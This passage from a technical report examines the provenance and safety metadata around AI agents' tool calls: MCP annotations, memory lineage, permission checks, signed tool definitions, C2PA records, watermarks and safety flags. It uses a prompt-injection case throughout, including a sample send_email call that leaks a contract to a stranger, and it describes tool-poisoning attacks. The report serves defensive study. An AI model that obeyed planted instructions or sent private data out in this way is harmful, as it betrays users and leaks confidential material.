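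The proposal also allows a separate label on each item in a mixed result, such as a list of search hits. This addresses a gap left by roles, but it helps only if the client can keep the items apart. Once the model has read them all in one context, the cautious rule combines their labels again.

None of the five fields directly marks which text the model may obey. `openWorldHint` comes closest, but the Model Context Protocol project warns that its meaning depends on the setting, since "external" could mean outside the company's network or outside one laptop. The project says it is safest to treat anything external as possibly untrusted. The definition matters because a server that treated the firm's mail as a closed system would mark a fraudster's email on the firm's own mail server as internal.

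All of these fields are self-reported. This does little harm in the supplier's case, because an honest tool server can mark the page as open-world without having noticed the hidden sentence. But a dishonest server could mark its own planted text as internal and harmless. The labels also don't make the model less susceptible to such text. They work only if the client acts on them, and the project recommends network controls or sandboxing (running a program where it can't reach anything else) for anything that needs a guarantee.

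SEP-1913 has made slow progress. It was a draft in March 2026 and still a draft on 20 April, when Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* set up a group to study this and similar proposals. The charter leaves open whether tool responses should have annotations at all. SEP-1913 is not in the project's index of accepted and final proposals, which has entries up to 5 October 2026. In *added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK*, kapil8811, a group member from Microsoft, submitted trial code that extends the idea with categories such as medical, financial and login data, the destinations of inputs and outputs, and the severity of an action's outcome. Its examples include a clinic's server with eight annotated tools.

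### Labels in an agent's memory

Many agents save notes for later sessions, and a label is useless if the agent saves the text without it. Suppose the employee's assistant had included the hidden sentence in a saved summary of the supplier's terms instead of obeying it at once. A month later, the assistant would find the summary among its own notes, with no record that the sentence came from the web page.

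MemLineage, the system that Ouyang and Hou built, keeps the trace. Each saved note is a record containing:

- an identifier, the content, and the writer (the user, an agent, a tool or an outside source);
- a hash of the source data and a hash of everything in the prompt at the time of writing;
- a trust level;
- a list of parents, meaning the earlier notes that the new one drew on, with a weight from 0 to 1 for each;
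- a timestamp, a random number that makes the record unique, and the writer's digital signature over all the rest.

The four trust levels are Trusted (0), Derived-Trusted (1), Derived-Untrusted (2) and External (3). A new note takes the least trusted level among the parents whose weight exceeds a chosen threshold. The agent may still use an untrusted note to answer questions. Before a sensitive action, such as sending email or moving money, a gate checks the notes the call is based on and can refuse the call, ask the user, or replace a suspect argument with one from a trusted source.

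One of their experiments closely resembles the supplier's case. In one session an agent summarises an outside vendor's document into memory, and in a later session it retrieves only the summary and proposes an email. A defence that checked only signatures let the email go, because the summary had a valid signature. MemLineage blocked it because the record still linked the summary to the document. With live models and no defence, gpt-5.3-codex sent the email in 5 of 20 trials and gpt-5.4-mini in 2 of 10. With MemLineage neither model sent it, although with so few trials the true rate for gpt-5.3-codex could be as high as 16%.

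MemLineage also stopped all the attacks in both sets of six banking tasks. In the ordinary set, the version that repairs arguments completed five of the six tasks, compared with two with no defence. However, the repairs relied on the benchmark's own correct bill details, which stood in for a trusted source such as a bank's invoice system. A real deployment would first have to label such sources reliably.

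The weights are MemLineage's weak point. The simplest version gives every note in the context a weight of 1, which brings back the problem of everything becoming untrusted. A second model can instead score how much each parent influenced the new note. Ouyang and Hou simulated a scorer whose confidence starts at 0.9 and falls by 30% with each further summary, giving 0.90, 0.63, 0.44, 0.31 and 0.22. With a threshold of 0.3, the External label survives four rounds of summarising and disappears in the fifth. A note with no parent above the threshold counts as Trusted, so an attacker's text is labelled Trusted if it survives enough rewording. A note also counts as Trusted if the agent saves it without listing its parents. Stricter settings closed these gaps in the tests, but one of them also blocked a legitimate reminder to send an email, because the reminder had no parent to show that it could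 be trusted.

### Inferring the attributes instead

Labels require cooperation from every server and client that handles the data. MetaPermit needs much less, and it is the best argument that a schema need not carry them. Before each tool call, a model answers five questions with values from a fixed list:

1. Does the user want an action, or only a conversation?
2. Is the user's goal clear?
3. Does the action risk irreversible harm or the disclosure of private data?
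4. Does the tool serve the user's goal?
5. Does the user's request justify the arguments of the call?

A fixed set of rules uses the answers to allow or deny the call. The first two answers depend only on the user's request, so planted text can't affect them. In the supplier's case, the employee never mentioned the stranger and the fifth answer would be no, so the rules would deny the call. They would allow the email to Priya, even though the agent had read an untrusted page.

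The results support the approach on ordinary tasks. With MiniMax-M2.7 on AgentDojo, the agent completed 69.4% of tasks with MetaPermit and 72.0% with no defence. Ma and colleagues checked the few attacks that the benchmark had counted as successes with that model and found that the agent had mentioned the attacker's target in its reasoning but never made the call. They also gave MetaPermit 95 malicious calls, bypassing the agent, with a planted prompt that disclosed the rules and asked for favourable answers. MetaPermit allowed none of the calls, although the prompt lowered the risk answer in 17% of cases.

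It does worse on open-ended work. With Qwen3, completion fell from 45% to 9% on AgentDyn's shopping tasks and from 69% to 19% on its GitHub tasks. When a user asks an agent to follow the steps in a document, the request doesn't mention the arguments those steps need, so a check against the request alone has little to compare them with. A label showing that the document had authority could help, but CaMeL scored zero on the same tasks, which suggests that labels alone won't solve the problem.

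The decisions also vary between runs. Ma and colleagues ran each of 50 queries 20 times, and the verdict was the same every time for only 42% of the queries. For a model that gave the verdict directly, the figure was 32%. Fixed rules applied to fixed labels would give the same answer in every run, and an investigator could check it afterwards.

Some facts can't be inferred from the conversation. Alex's request to answer some emails doesn't reveal that Marco isn't allowed to see the sales figures, because that fact is in the company's access records. Or suppose the hidden sentence on the supplier's page had read "Priya's address has changed" and given a new one. The employee asked for an email to Priya, so a model might well judge the new address justified. But a label on the `to` argument would show that the address came from a web page.

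MetaPermit also treats the user's request as trusted, so it still depends on the schema to identify that request. If the employee pastes in an email from the supplier that contains a hidden instruction, the whole message has the role `user`, and MetaPermit would check the agent's actions against the attacker's words as well as the employee's.

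## Identifying tools and what they can do

The third question about the stray email was which tool sent it, who operates that tool, and what else it could have done. The employee's app called `send_email`, but many servers may offer a tool with that name. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (Metere, 2026) describes an attack in which a malicious server copies a legitimate tool's name so that the client sends calls to the malicious server instead. To rule this out, an investigator would need to know which server supplied the tool, who runs that server, which version was running, and what tool description the model had read.

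### What the record of a call contains

A tool call in Chat Completions identifies the tool only by name, so the provider can't tell whether `send_email` is a few lines of code inside the deployer's app or another company's server. The provider does have the tool's description, because the deployer sends it with the request.

OpenAI and Anthropic can also connect to an MCP server themselves, and the model's output then includes more about the call. With Anthropic's *MCP connector*, the record of the stray email would look roughly like this:

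```json
{
  "type": "mcp_tool_use",
  "id": "mcptoolu_01...",
  "name": "send_email",
  "server_name": "office-mail",
  "input": {"to": "stranger@elsewhere.example", "body": "..."}
}
```

The `server_name` is a label the deployer chose when configuring the connection, so a deployer could call any server `office-mail`. OpenAI's equivalent, `mcp_call`, has a similar `server_label`. It also holds the output, any error, and the ID of any approval request, according to *Class ResponseItem.McpCall*, a reference page for OpenAI's Java toolkit. Neither format has a field for the server's operator or version. The deployer's request contains the server's web address, which is the best clue to the operator, but a monitor who keeps only the model's output will not have it. OpenAI warns that it has not verified remote MCP servers.

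In MCP, a call doesn't need to name the server, because the client sends it to a particular one. The server's reply should include `serverInfo`, which gives the server's name and version. Like `clientInfo`, this field is self-reported. The July 2026 Model Context Protocol specification describes both fields as intended for display, logging and debugging, and warns against relying on them for security.

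| | Chat Completions | OpenAI `mcp_call` | Anthropic `mcp_tool_use` | MCP `tools/call` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Server | no field | deployer's label | deployer's label | self-reported, in the reply |
| Operator | no field | no field | no field | no field |
| Version | no field | no field | no field | self-reported, in the reply |
| Description the model read | in the request | in a separate `mcp_list_tools` item | in a separate `mcp_tool_listing` item (beta) | in an earlier reply that lists the tools |

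Even an investigator who knows the server's name can't look up what its tools did on a given date. In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) examined all 21,643 servers in MCP's public registry in August 2026 and found that the registry stores no tool definitions. Of the 8,900 servers with more than one published version, 40.6% had changed their description or where a package or address pointed, while every identifier stayed the same. The registry entries for 370 servers had changed to an address on a different host. Kraishan thinks most of these changes were routine migrations, but neither the registry nor a client can distinguish a migration from a takeover.

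*OpenAgenet* (2026), a proposed directory of agent services, would store each tool with its server, its package version and a hash of its contents. If a call record included that hash, an investigator could find the exact tool definition that was in use. The directory would also keep a server's claims about itself separate from facts the network has verified.

### Four hints about behaviour

Since March 2025, MCP has had four optional true-or-false annotations that describe what a tool does. A server sends them with the tool's definition.

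| Hint | What "true" means | If missing, assume | Possible response by a client |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool changes nothing | false | Skip the confirmation if true |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, not just add to it | true | Warn the user if true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments is safe | false | Retry after a failure if true |
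| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside systems or people | true | Check the output for untrusted content if true |

The defaults are cautious, so a client should assume that an unmarked tool can change or destroy things, do further damage if called twice, and reach the outside world.

Many tools have no hints. Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, collected the definitions of 98,291 tools from remote servers in the registry and found at least one hint on 74.0% of them. One publisher supplied 45% of the tools and filled in all four hints on each. Without that publisher, the share falls to 52.8%. Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, drew 400 locally installed servers at random, of which 195 started. Of their 2,766 tools, 58.8% had no hints. On every server with tools, either all of the tools had hints or none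 did, which suggests that hints are missing mostly because some server authors never use them.

Clients also tend to ignore the cautious defaults. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) traced what happens to an ordinary MCP call in 41 open-source clients (25 applications and 16 developer toolkits). Of these, 32 have no approval step unless someone configures one. In 39, marking a tool destructive changed nothing. Only Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, used a combination of hints to decide whether to ask the user, although VS Code skips the question for tools marked read-only.

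A server can also ask the user for confirmation through the client, but Yao and colleagues estimate that 90% of destructive tools have no confirmation step on the server. They paired a sample of such tools with the 25 applications and calculated how different rules would change the outcome. The last column covers tools that their software flagged as destructive but that turned out not to be.

| Rule | Destructive tools that run without approval | Other tools for which someone must approve |
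|---|---|---|
| Current defaults | 60.7% | 32.5% |
| Every client passes servers' questions on to the user | 56.7% | 35.2% |
| Every client asks unless the tool is marked read-only or non-destructive | 5.4% | 82.6% |

These are shares of application–tool pairs, not of calls or users. Adding seven closed-source applications lowers the current figure to 47.5%. The 5.4% is also too low for tools in general, because the software that picked the sample missed many destructive ones. Still, following MCP's existing defaults would clearly make a large difference. It would also interrupt people much more often, and those who have to approve nearly everything may stop reading the questions.

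The supplier's case shows a weakness in the third rule. MCP contrasts "destructive" with "additive", so a tool's author could honestly mark `send_email` as non-destructive because sending a message deletes nothing. A client that followed the rule would then send the contract without asking. Codex CLI would still ask, because it runs a non-destructive tool without asking only if the tool is also read-only or doesn't reach external systems.

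MCP has no field to indicate whether the client has already asked the user to approve a call. The server must therefore ask the user, possibly for a second time, refuse the call, or run it without confirmation that the user was asked. Yao and colleagues suggest that clients declare whether they obtain human approval, so that a server would need to refuse only when nobody was asked.

Some servers require the model to set an argument such as `confirm=true`. In tests with planted instructions, models set this argument by themselves in 127 of 169 attempts to delete the wrong note, even though the planted text hadn't mentioned it. Finding `confirm=true` in a log is therefore not evidence that a person agreed.

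The hints also lack the detail needed to reconstruct what a tool did. In Trofimov and Novikov's example, an agent pays an invoice, receives no acknowledgement and pays again. `idempotentHint` can mark a repeated payment as safe, but the hints include no ID that would let the server recognise the second call as a repeat, and no way to ask whether the first one succeeded. Someone investigating two `send_email` calls would likewise need the mail server's records to find out how many emails went out.

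### The dispute over hints that nobody can check

A dishonest server can label a tool read-only even if the tool deletes files. When contributors first proposed such hints, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, agreed that the information would be very useful if clients could trust it, but wondered how they could use it otherwise. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even a tool's display title. Model Context Protocol recounts that the compromise was to call every annotation a hint and require clients to treat hints as untrusted by default. Each client then decides how much weight to give them, based on the information it has about the server.

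For an untrusted server, Hosmer's position follows almost directly from the defaults. If a client assumes the worst about an unmarked tool, a hint can only make the tool look safer, and a dishonest server would fake exactly that kind of hint. The hints are useful when the client has another reason to trust the server, such as when one company runs both. In a client that ignores the defaults, `destructiveHint: true` could also trigger a warning that would otherwise not appear, but Yao and colleagues found almost no clients that work this way.

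SEP-1913, written by contributors from GitHub and OpenAI, proposes more annotations. By March 2026 it was one of five open proposals, which also included hints for secrets and for unsafe output. The main argument for more annotations is that a hint that isn't fully reliable can still be useful if a client combines it with other evidence, such as a company's own list of approved servers.

Large companies want a richer vocabulary of annotations, while developers of autonomous agents often think confirmations slow their agents down and rely on sandboxes. When the maintainers reviewed the proposals, no MCP client let users filter tools by annotation or showed annotations in its approval prompts. New hints would probably do little until clients make better use of the existing four.

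The maintainers offered five questions for judging a proposed annotation:

1. **What client behaviour does it enable?** If a client would do nothing differently, the annotation probably doesn't belong in the protocol. Jonathan Hefner, a maintainer, raised this objection to an early draft of one of the five proposals.
2. **Does it need trust to be useful?** A wrong title does little harm, but a client that skips a confirmation has to believe `readOnlyHint`.
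3. **Could `_meta` handle it instead?** A company that runs both client and server can use a private field there and gather evidence before proposing a standard one.
4. **Does it help a client reason about combinations of tools?**
5. **Is it a hint or a contract?** If an annotation is worthless unless true, enforcement belongs elsewhere, such as in the authorisation system.

The first question puts monitors at a disadvantage. A field identifying the server's operator could fail the test because it might not change what any client does during a call, but an investigator might need it more than any of the four existing hints.

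### Risk depends on the other tools

Whether a tool that searches an inbox is dangerous depends on the agent's other tools, because different tools can supply the three parts of the lethal trifecta. In one demonstration, researchers planted instructions in the description of a Google Calendar event. The agent read the event through an MCP calendar server and had a separate tool that could run code on the user's machine. These two tools were enough to complete the attack.

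A single MCP server rarely has all the tools that a data theft requires. *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) examined 1,360 servers and found 370 with at least one tool that could read outside content, read private data or send data out. Only two servers had tools for all three. The full combination therefore usually arises when a user connects several servers to one agent, and each server's operator knows only about that server's tools. Even if every server provided accurate hints, the client would still have to work out the risk of the whole set.

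Tools are also becoming more powerful. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi, 2026) cites an analysis of 177,436 tools, which found that those that directly change outside systems rose from 27% to 65% of usage between November 2024 and February 2026.

In the employee's request to the model, the `tools` list contains `fetch_page`, `search_files` and `send_email`. A monitor at the deployer or the provider could recognise the dangerous combination from that list before the model called any of the tools. The mail server's operator would receive only the `send_email` call. An investigator needs the full list of available tools to determine what else the agent could have done, and a log of only the calls doesn't include it.

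### Signed tool definitions

An attacker who takes over an approved server can add instructions for the model to a tool's description, a technique security researchers call tool poisoning. *Tool Metadata Poisoning* cites success rates of 91–96% in demonstrations against MCP clients. Kraishan scanned the code of 14,353 servers and found no cases, but the scan searched for known patterns and would have missed disguised instructions, so the real frequency of tool poisoning is unknown.

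*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP, points out that the protocol has no built-in way for a client to check whether a tool's definition has changed since somebody approved it. One remedy is for the publisher to sign the definition. In *ETDI* (2025), an early design, the signature covers the tool's name, description, input and output formats, version and required permissions, and the client checks the signature when it discovers the tool.

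*Tool Metadata Poisoning* presents a later scheme, CTMS, that covers seven fields: the name, title, description, input format, output format, annotations and execution settings. The publisher's software writes these fields in a fixed order, so the same definition always produces the same data, and hashes that data. The publisher signs the result through Sigstore, a service that ties a signature to an existing login, such as a GitHub account, and records it in a public log that allows only additions. When a client receives the definition from a server, it repeats the calculation and blocks the tool if the hash differs.

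In a demonstration, the software accepted an unchanged definition and rejected four altered ones. The alterations were a planted instruction, a subtle rewording, an extra input that would collect the user's messages, and a missing `readOnlyHint`. Any change to the seven fields alters the hash, so the demonstration shows that the software works as designed, but not how it would perform in wide use.

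A valid signature proves that the named publisher signed this exact definition, but not that the definition is true. A tool described as reading files could delete them and still pass the signature check. The signature also doesn't cover the server's code, so the server's operator can change what the tool does without invalidating the signature.

### Pinning on first use

A client can detect changes to a tool's definition without the publisher's help. It saves the definition, or a hash of it, when the user first approves the server, and compares later definitions with that copy. The security company Trail of Bits offers a free program that sits between a client and a server and does this. The company's *Model Context Protocol* describes how the program requires manual approval before a changed description can reach the model.

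Pinning proves only that the definition is the same as the one the client first saw. If the server was malicious from the start, the client pins the malicious version. Users could also tire of approving frequent updates. Among the registry's servers that had changed their entries, Kraishan found a median gap of one day between changed versions. Tool definitions may change less often than registry entries, but a user with a dozen servers could still face regular requests to approve harmless edits.

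In September 2026, Anthropic released a beta feature that records the tool list a server returns and keeps using it for the rest of the conversation if the deployer sends it back with each request. The deployer can also fix the list permanently. Reusing the recorded list prevents a server from changing the descriptions Claude reads partway through a task, and it leaves a monitor with a copy of them. However, if the server changes a tool after the list is recorded, Claude will read an outdated description. The recorded entries also contain only each tool's name, description and input format, not its behaviour hints.

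### Attested admission of tool servers

Metere's system addresses an earlier decision, which is whether a client should use a server at all. The server publishes a small signed document at a fixed web address. The document contains the server's identity, publisher and version, and the most sensitive class of data that it may handle. Before the first call, the client checks that:

- it already trusts the signer's key, which hasn't expired;
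- the signer has the authority to approve servers for that class of data;
- the signature is valid;
- the approved class is high enough for the task;
- the document came from an address that it covers, if it lists any.

For each admitted server, the client keeps a list of permitted tools and refuses calls to any other tool before sending anything. It also logs every decision and links each log entry to the previous one by a hash, so that an auditor can detect a deletion.

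Metere had a language model generate attacks on both checks. The client rejected all 27,025 distinct tool names designed to get past the list and all 14,378 forged documents. A perfect score was expected, because the client accepts only exact matches from the list and the attacking model had no trusted key to sign documents with. Any accepted attack would have meant a programming error. Metere works for Enclawed, the company that develops the system.

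In a live test with Google's Gmail server, the client allowed a permitted tool and blocked another. But Google doesn't publish the signed document, so the client relied on its own signed configuration file. Public MCP servers have little reason to publish such a document until many clients check for it, which is why Metere wants MCP to adopt a common format.

A successful check proves that a signer the client trusts has approved this server for a certain class of data. The list of tools limits what a hijacked model can call. Neither prevents an approved server from misusing a permitted tool or changing its behaviour after admission.

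None of the three kinds of check would have stopped the theft of the contract, because `send_email` was a genuine, unchanged tool on an approved server, and the employee needed it for the email to Priya. The results of the checks could still help an investigator establish which tool sent the contract, but only if the client kept them with the call. Neither `mcp_call` nor `mcp_tool_use` has a field for them.

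## Recording where documents, images and generated content came from

The fourth question about the stray email was where the planted sentence and the attached contract came from. The model had read both as text in tool results, and a Chat Completions tool message has no field for a page's address or a file's history. Images and documents can store that history in the file itself, using an open standard. Copying text usually removes any record of its origin, and the watermarks that AI companies have begun adding to generated text reveal very little.

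### How a C2PA record works

The Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA) publishes the standard, which grew out of projects at Adobe, the BBC and Microsoft. Its records are called manifests or Content Credentials. The first consumer camera to write them was a Leica released in October 2023, according to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026). Adobe's editing software and some AI image generators now write them too.

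Suppose a worker in the firm's warehouse photographs a damaged delivery with such a camera. The camera creates the record in four steps:

1. It writes assertions, which are statements about the picture, such as when and on what device the worker took it.
2. It computes a hash of the picture and adds this as a further assertion, which ties the record to this picture and no other.
3. It wraps the assertions in what C2PA's *Content Credentials*, the technical specification, calls a claim, and signs the claim.
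4. It stores the record in the image file.

In simplified form, the result looks like this:

```json
{
  "assertions": [
    {"label": "c2pa.actions.v2",
     "actions": [{"action": "c2pa.created",
                  "digitalSourceType": "digitalCapture"}]},
    {"label": "c2pa.hash.data", "alg": "sha256", "hash": "b41f..."}
  ],
  "claim": {"generator": "Camera firmware 2.1", "assertion_hashes": ["..."]},
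  "signature": "..."
}
```

If an AI system had made the picture, `digitalSourceType` would record that. C2PA's *Use of Content Credentials to Identify Synthetic and Non Synthetic Content* (2026) also describes a separate assertion for disclosing AI use and a way to mark which regions of a picture AI changed.

When someone edits the photo in software that supports the standard, the software adds a new record and keeps the camera's record as an "ingredient". The new file doesn't usually contain the original picture, so nobody can check the camera's hash again later. The editing software does that check at the time of the edit and records the result. Anyone who receives the edited photo has to rely on the software for everything that happened before the edit.

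### What a valid record proves

A checker can establish whether anyone has altered the record since signing, whether the file matches it, and whether the signer is on a list of trusted signers. These checks don't establish that the picture gives a true account, because the camera would have produced the same valid record if the worker had damaged the delivery on purpose. *Trustworthy synthetic visual media* (2026) points out that a signature also can't reveal events that nobody recorded.

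*Media Integrity and Authentication* (2026) notes that people can add records to existing files, and that the signer of a record can state whatever they choose about the file's origin. The signer's identity is then a verified field, but the statements are still self-reported.

The hash may also protect less of the file than users expect. C2PA's introductory guide says that any alteration, however insignificant, would break the match between file and record. But *Verifying Provenance of Digital Media* (2026), a critique of the standard, explains that the hash leaves out an "exclusion range", where changes go undetected. Some exclusion is unavoidable, because a record inside a file can't contain a hash of itself. The paper's criticism is that other metadata in the file can also go unprotected. A tool can protect this metadata by copying it into an assertion, which C2PA allows but doesn't require.

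### A signed photo sent to a model

Suppose the worker then asks the firm's assistant to brighten the photo. In a Chat Completions message, an image has one field for its data or URL and another for the level of detail, but none for its history. The camera's record arrives inside the file if the app sends the original, but it will probably be lost if the app first shrinks or converts the picture.

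Neither OpenAI's help page on provenance nor Anthropic's *How Claude marks AI-generated content* explains what happens to the provenance record on an image that a customer sends in. Vision models work from pixels, so a model would receive the record only if the provider's software read it and added its contents to the prompt. A deployer that needs the record should keep the original file and assume that the model hasn't received the record.

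The deployer can have a file checked in a separate request. OpenAI's *Content provenance* documents a service that looks for OpenAI's own marks in images and audio. For the worker's photo, the C2PA part of the result might be:

```json
{
  "type": "c2pa",
  "outcome": "not_detected",
  "validation_state": "trusted",
  "issuer": "Example Camera Company",
  "model": null,
  "generated_at": null
}
```

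The photo has a valid record, but `outcome` is `not_detected` because OpenAI didn't issue that record. A monitor that logged only `outcome` couldn't distinguish this photo from one with no record. The deployer receives the result, but the request to the model has no standard field for it.

Brightening a picture gives it a new record. OpenAI adds a C2PA record and an invisible watermark called SynthID to images from ChatGPT and its API, except those from a few models it is about to retire. Anthropic attaches C2PA records to supported file types that Claude creates, such as PNG and JPEG. OpenAI's record can include the model and the time of generation, so it is more useful to an investigator than any mark on text.

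The new record could include the camera's record as an ingredient, but neither company says whether its tools do this. If the tools leave it out, an insurer that received the brightened photo might learn only that an OpenAI tool had processed it. OpenAI warns that its marks alone don't show how much of a file its tools generated or edited, so a harmless edit could make a genuine photo look more suspicious.

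### Survival on platforms

Most ways of uploading a file strip C2PA records, according to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, and so do screenshots and re-encoding. Adobe's Content Authenticity Initiative, which promotes the standard, concedes in *The three pillars of provenance that make up durable Content Credentials* that platforms still commonly remove metadata, despite adoption by companies such as LinkedIn and TikTok.

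Precise figures on how many records survive uploading are harder to find. IPTC, a standards body for the news industry, checks images that it collects online. Its *C2PA content credentials* reports records in 15 of the 6,845 images checked between May and July 2026, or 0.22%. This shows how rarely a monitor can expect to find a record, but it isn't a survival rate, because most of those images may never have had a record. To measure survival, someone would have to upload files with known records, download them again and compare them with the originals.

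A platform can also receive metadata and ignore it. IPTC's *AI disclosure on social media* describes a March 2026 study by the publication Indicator in which Instagram recognised some images from Meta's AI as AI-generated, but LinkedIn, TikTok and YouTube didn't. Meta had marked the images with an IPTC metadata field instead of a C2PA record, and IPTC concludes that the other platforms don't check that field.

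C2PA addresses stripping by adding a second link between a file and its record. A tool hides an identifier in the picture as a watermark, or computes a fingerprint of how the picture looks, and stores a copy of the record online. If a platform removes the record from the file, a checker can use the watermark or fingerprint to find the online copy. This works only if someone maintains that copy and the checker knows where to look. Heavy cropping or compression can also destroy a watermark.

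A monitor can conclude very little when it finds no provenance record. Asked whether people should distrust media without one, C2PA answers "Maybe", because using its standard is optional.

### Forged and identifying records

Anyone can create a false record and sign it with their own key. The list of trusted signers is meant to expose this, since a checker will find that the signature is valid but the signer is not on it. The list helps less when an attacker gets a trusted device to sign something false. Nikon added C2PA to its Z6 III camera in August 2025 and then suspended the feature because of a flaw in the signing process. SoftwareSeni's *C2PA Adoption in 2026* reports that all the certificates were revoked and that the service was still unavailable in early 2026. Checkers can use revocation to spot forgeries, but it may also lead them to doubt honest photographers' pictures.

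Other critics worry that the records will reveal too much. *Unia każe oznaczać treści AI* (2026), an article in the Polish daily Rzeczpospolita, warned that companies or governments could use the standard to track people. C2PA replies that its core specification doesn't cover the identity of people or organisations and leaves that to optional extensions. Its guide gives the example of a human rights group that receives footage of police violence and protects the identity of the person who filmed it by removing details about them. Times and device details could still help link one person's files.

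Anthropic's provenance records contain no identifying information about the user, according to its *Check if a file was made with Claude*, and OpenAI's marks include no details of the user, organisation or prompt. This protects users, but an investigator can't trace an AI-made file to an account from the mark alone.

### Source fields in search results

AI interfaces have fields for the origin of text mainly when the provider runs a search for the model. In OpenAI's Responses API, a web citation contains the page's address and title, and marks where the passage it supports starts and ends in the answer. Anthropic's citations also quote the source. When the source is an uploaded document, the citation identifies that instead of a web page.

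These fields would have been little help with the supplier's page. The employee's app fetched the page with its own tool, so any source field would have had to come from the app or the tool server. The `attribution` field proposed in SEP-1913 would give tool servers a standard place for it. Citations also support statements in an answer, not actions. A citation could have linked the prices in Priya's summary to the supplier's page, but it wouldn't have linked the hidden sentence to the email sent to the stranger.

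A page's address is also weak evidence months later, because the attacker may have deleted the sentence by then. An investigator would need a saved copy of the page as the model read it, or at least a hash of that version to check a copy found elsewhere. Even a saved copy wouldn't show whether a person or a model had written the sentence.

### What a text watermark can detect

OpenAI's text watermark, textGrain, slightly changes how a model chooses its words. At each step, a language model gives every possible next token a probability and picks one at random. textGrain creates several altered sets of these probabilities that average to the original set, and uses a secret key to select the set the model picks from.

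Suppose, with invented figures, that "cheap" and "inexpensive" each have a probability of 50%. One altered set gives them 80% and 20%, and the other gives them 20% and 80%. If the key selects the first set, the model will probably write "cheap". A reader without the key would notice nothing odd, but someone with it can count how often the text contains the favoured word. Over 100 such choices, ordinary text would contain it about 50 times and watermarked text about 80 times, a difference that is easy to detect. Over four choices, ordinary text would contain it at least three times in almost a third of cases, so the count could not show whether the text was watermarked.

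The example also explains why watermarks work badly on mathematics and code. If only one token is correct, no altered set can favour another.

OpenAI tuned its text watermark detector to wrongly flag 1% of unmarked passages. *OpenAI text watermark detection drops to 17% after 25% of words change* (Rijo, 2026) reports that, on psychology text, the detector then found the watermark in about 80% of passages of 200 tokens (roughly 150 words) and about 95% of those of 400 tokens. The main weakness is that detection drops to 17% after 25% of the words change. Results also vary by language. In a test on translated prompts, OpenAI detected the watermark in 69.0% of Spanish passages but only 42.2% of Romanian ones, before it strengthened the watermark for languages with lower detection rates.

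Even a 1% false alarm rate matters when most text is unmarked. If a monitor checked 10,000 passages of 200 tokens and 100 of them had the watermark, the detector would find about 80 of those and wrongly flag 99 others, so more than half of its alarms would be false. OpenAI cites false alarms and missed watermarks as its reason for not releasing the detector to the public.

A correct detection still doesn't show which model wrote a passage. OpenAI's detector reports only whether it finds an OpenAI watermark and doesn't look for other companies' marks, so a negative result doesn't mean a person wrote the text. A positive result doesn't prove that a model was the author, because people use models to proofread and translate their own work. Anthropic warns that such text can carry Claude's mark even if the ideas came from elsewhere. The provider's original response names the model in a separate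 field, but that field isn't copied when someone pastes the text into an email.

### What EU law requires

Article 50 of the EU's AI Act requires providers of generative AI to mark their output so that software can identify it as AI-generated. The duty has applied since 2 August 2026. Providers of older models have until 2 December 2026 to comply, according to Axios' *Anthropic's text watermarks signal new front in AI detection* (2026).

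Deployers have a separate duty to label deepfakes and AI-generated text published on matters of public interest. CEPA's *AI's Rubberstamp* notes an exception for content that has had genuine human review or editorial control. An invisible watermark doesn't satisfy the labeling duty because readers can't see it.

The European Commission published a code of practice on 10 June 2026 to help companies comply (*Commission publishes Code of Practice on marking and labelling AI-generated content*, 2026). The code is voluntary, but the law firm Jones Day expects it to become an important reference point for showing compliance (*European Commission Publishes Final Code of Practice*, 2026). OpenAI and Anthropic have both signed it but apply it differently.

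| | OpenAI | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|
| Text in its own apps | Watermark in the EU | Watermark worldwide, on supported models |
| Text through its API | Watermark only if the customer turns it on | Watermark worldwide, on supported models |
| Images and other files | C2PA record and watermark on images, watermark on audio, C2PA record on PDFs | C2PA record on supported files |
| Who can check text | Approved research and similar institutions | Eligible bodies such as regulators and newsrooms, and companies that must check their own output |

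Claude Sonnet 4.6 may not reliably add its watermark if the deployer changes `temperature`, a request field that controls how random the model's word choices are.

No single detector covers all providers. One criterion in the European Commission's (2026) study of text-marking methods was whether such a detector would be feasible. Until one exists, a monitor with a passage of unknown origin has to ask each company separately, and many monitors don't qualify for access.

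The code doesn't require watermarks in code snippets or in outputs shorter than 200 tokens. Even if the attacker had used ChatGPT to write the sentence hidden on the supplier's page, that sentence would have been far too short to need a watermark or for a detector to find one reliably.

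## Passing on earlier safety flags

The fifth question about the stray email was whether a filter or reviewer at any of the companies had already flagged the page, the request or the account. A safety flag is a recorded judgement that one of these may break the rules. Providers return many such flags to deployers, but common request formats have no field for passing them on.

### What a deployer gets back

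When one of Anthropic's safety classifiers declines a request, the response has the value `refusal` in `stop_reason`, the field that records why the model stopped. Anthropic's *Refusals and fallback* lists five possible categories for a refusal: cyber, biology, development of competing AI models, attempts to extract the model's reasoning, and general harms. The category can be empty, and there is no confidence score. According to Anthropic's *Stop reasons and fallback*, these details are empty for every other stop reason, so a request that narrowly passed the classifier looks like any other.

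OpenAI lets a deployer request moderation results along with the model's answer. The deployer gets a `flagged` value for the input and another for the output, with scores from 0 to 1 in 13 categories such as harassment, self-harm and violence. The model answers even if the input is flagged, and the deployer decides what to do. OpenAI reports its own enforcement separately, through error codes such as `cyber_policy`.

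Google reports safety filter results in two ways. For its cloud platform, *Safety and content filters* describes a reason code for each block, plus a probability score and a severity score for each of four harm categories. For the Interactions API, *Safety settings* describes an error for each blocked request, with a single code such as `safety` or `jailbreak` and no scores. In both, the adjustable filters are off by default for recent models.

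Microsoft's Azure rates text for hate, sexual content, violence and self-harm on a four-level severity scale and reports whether it filtered the text. Microsoft's *Guardrail annotations (classic)*, which covers the older version of its Foundry portal, also lists filters for attacks on the model. A deployer can set these filters to report an attack without blocking it.

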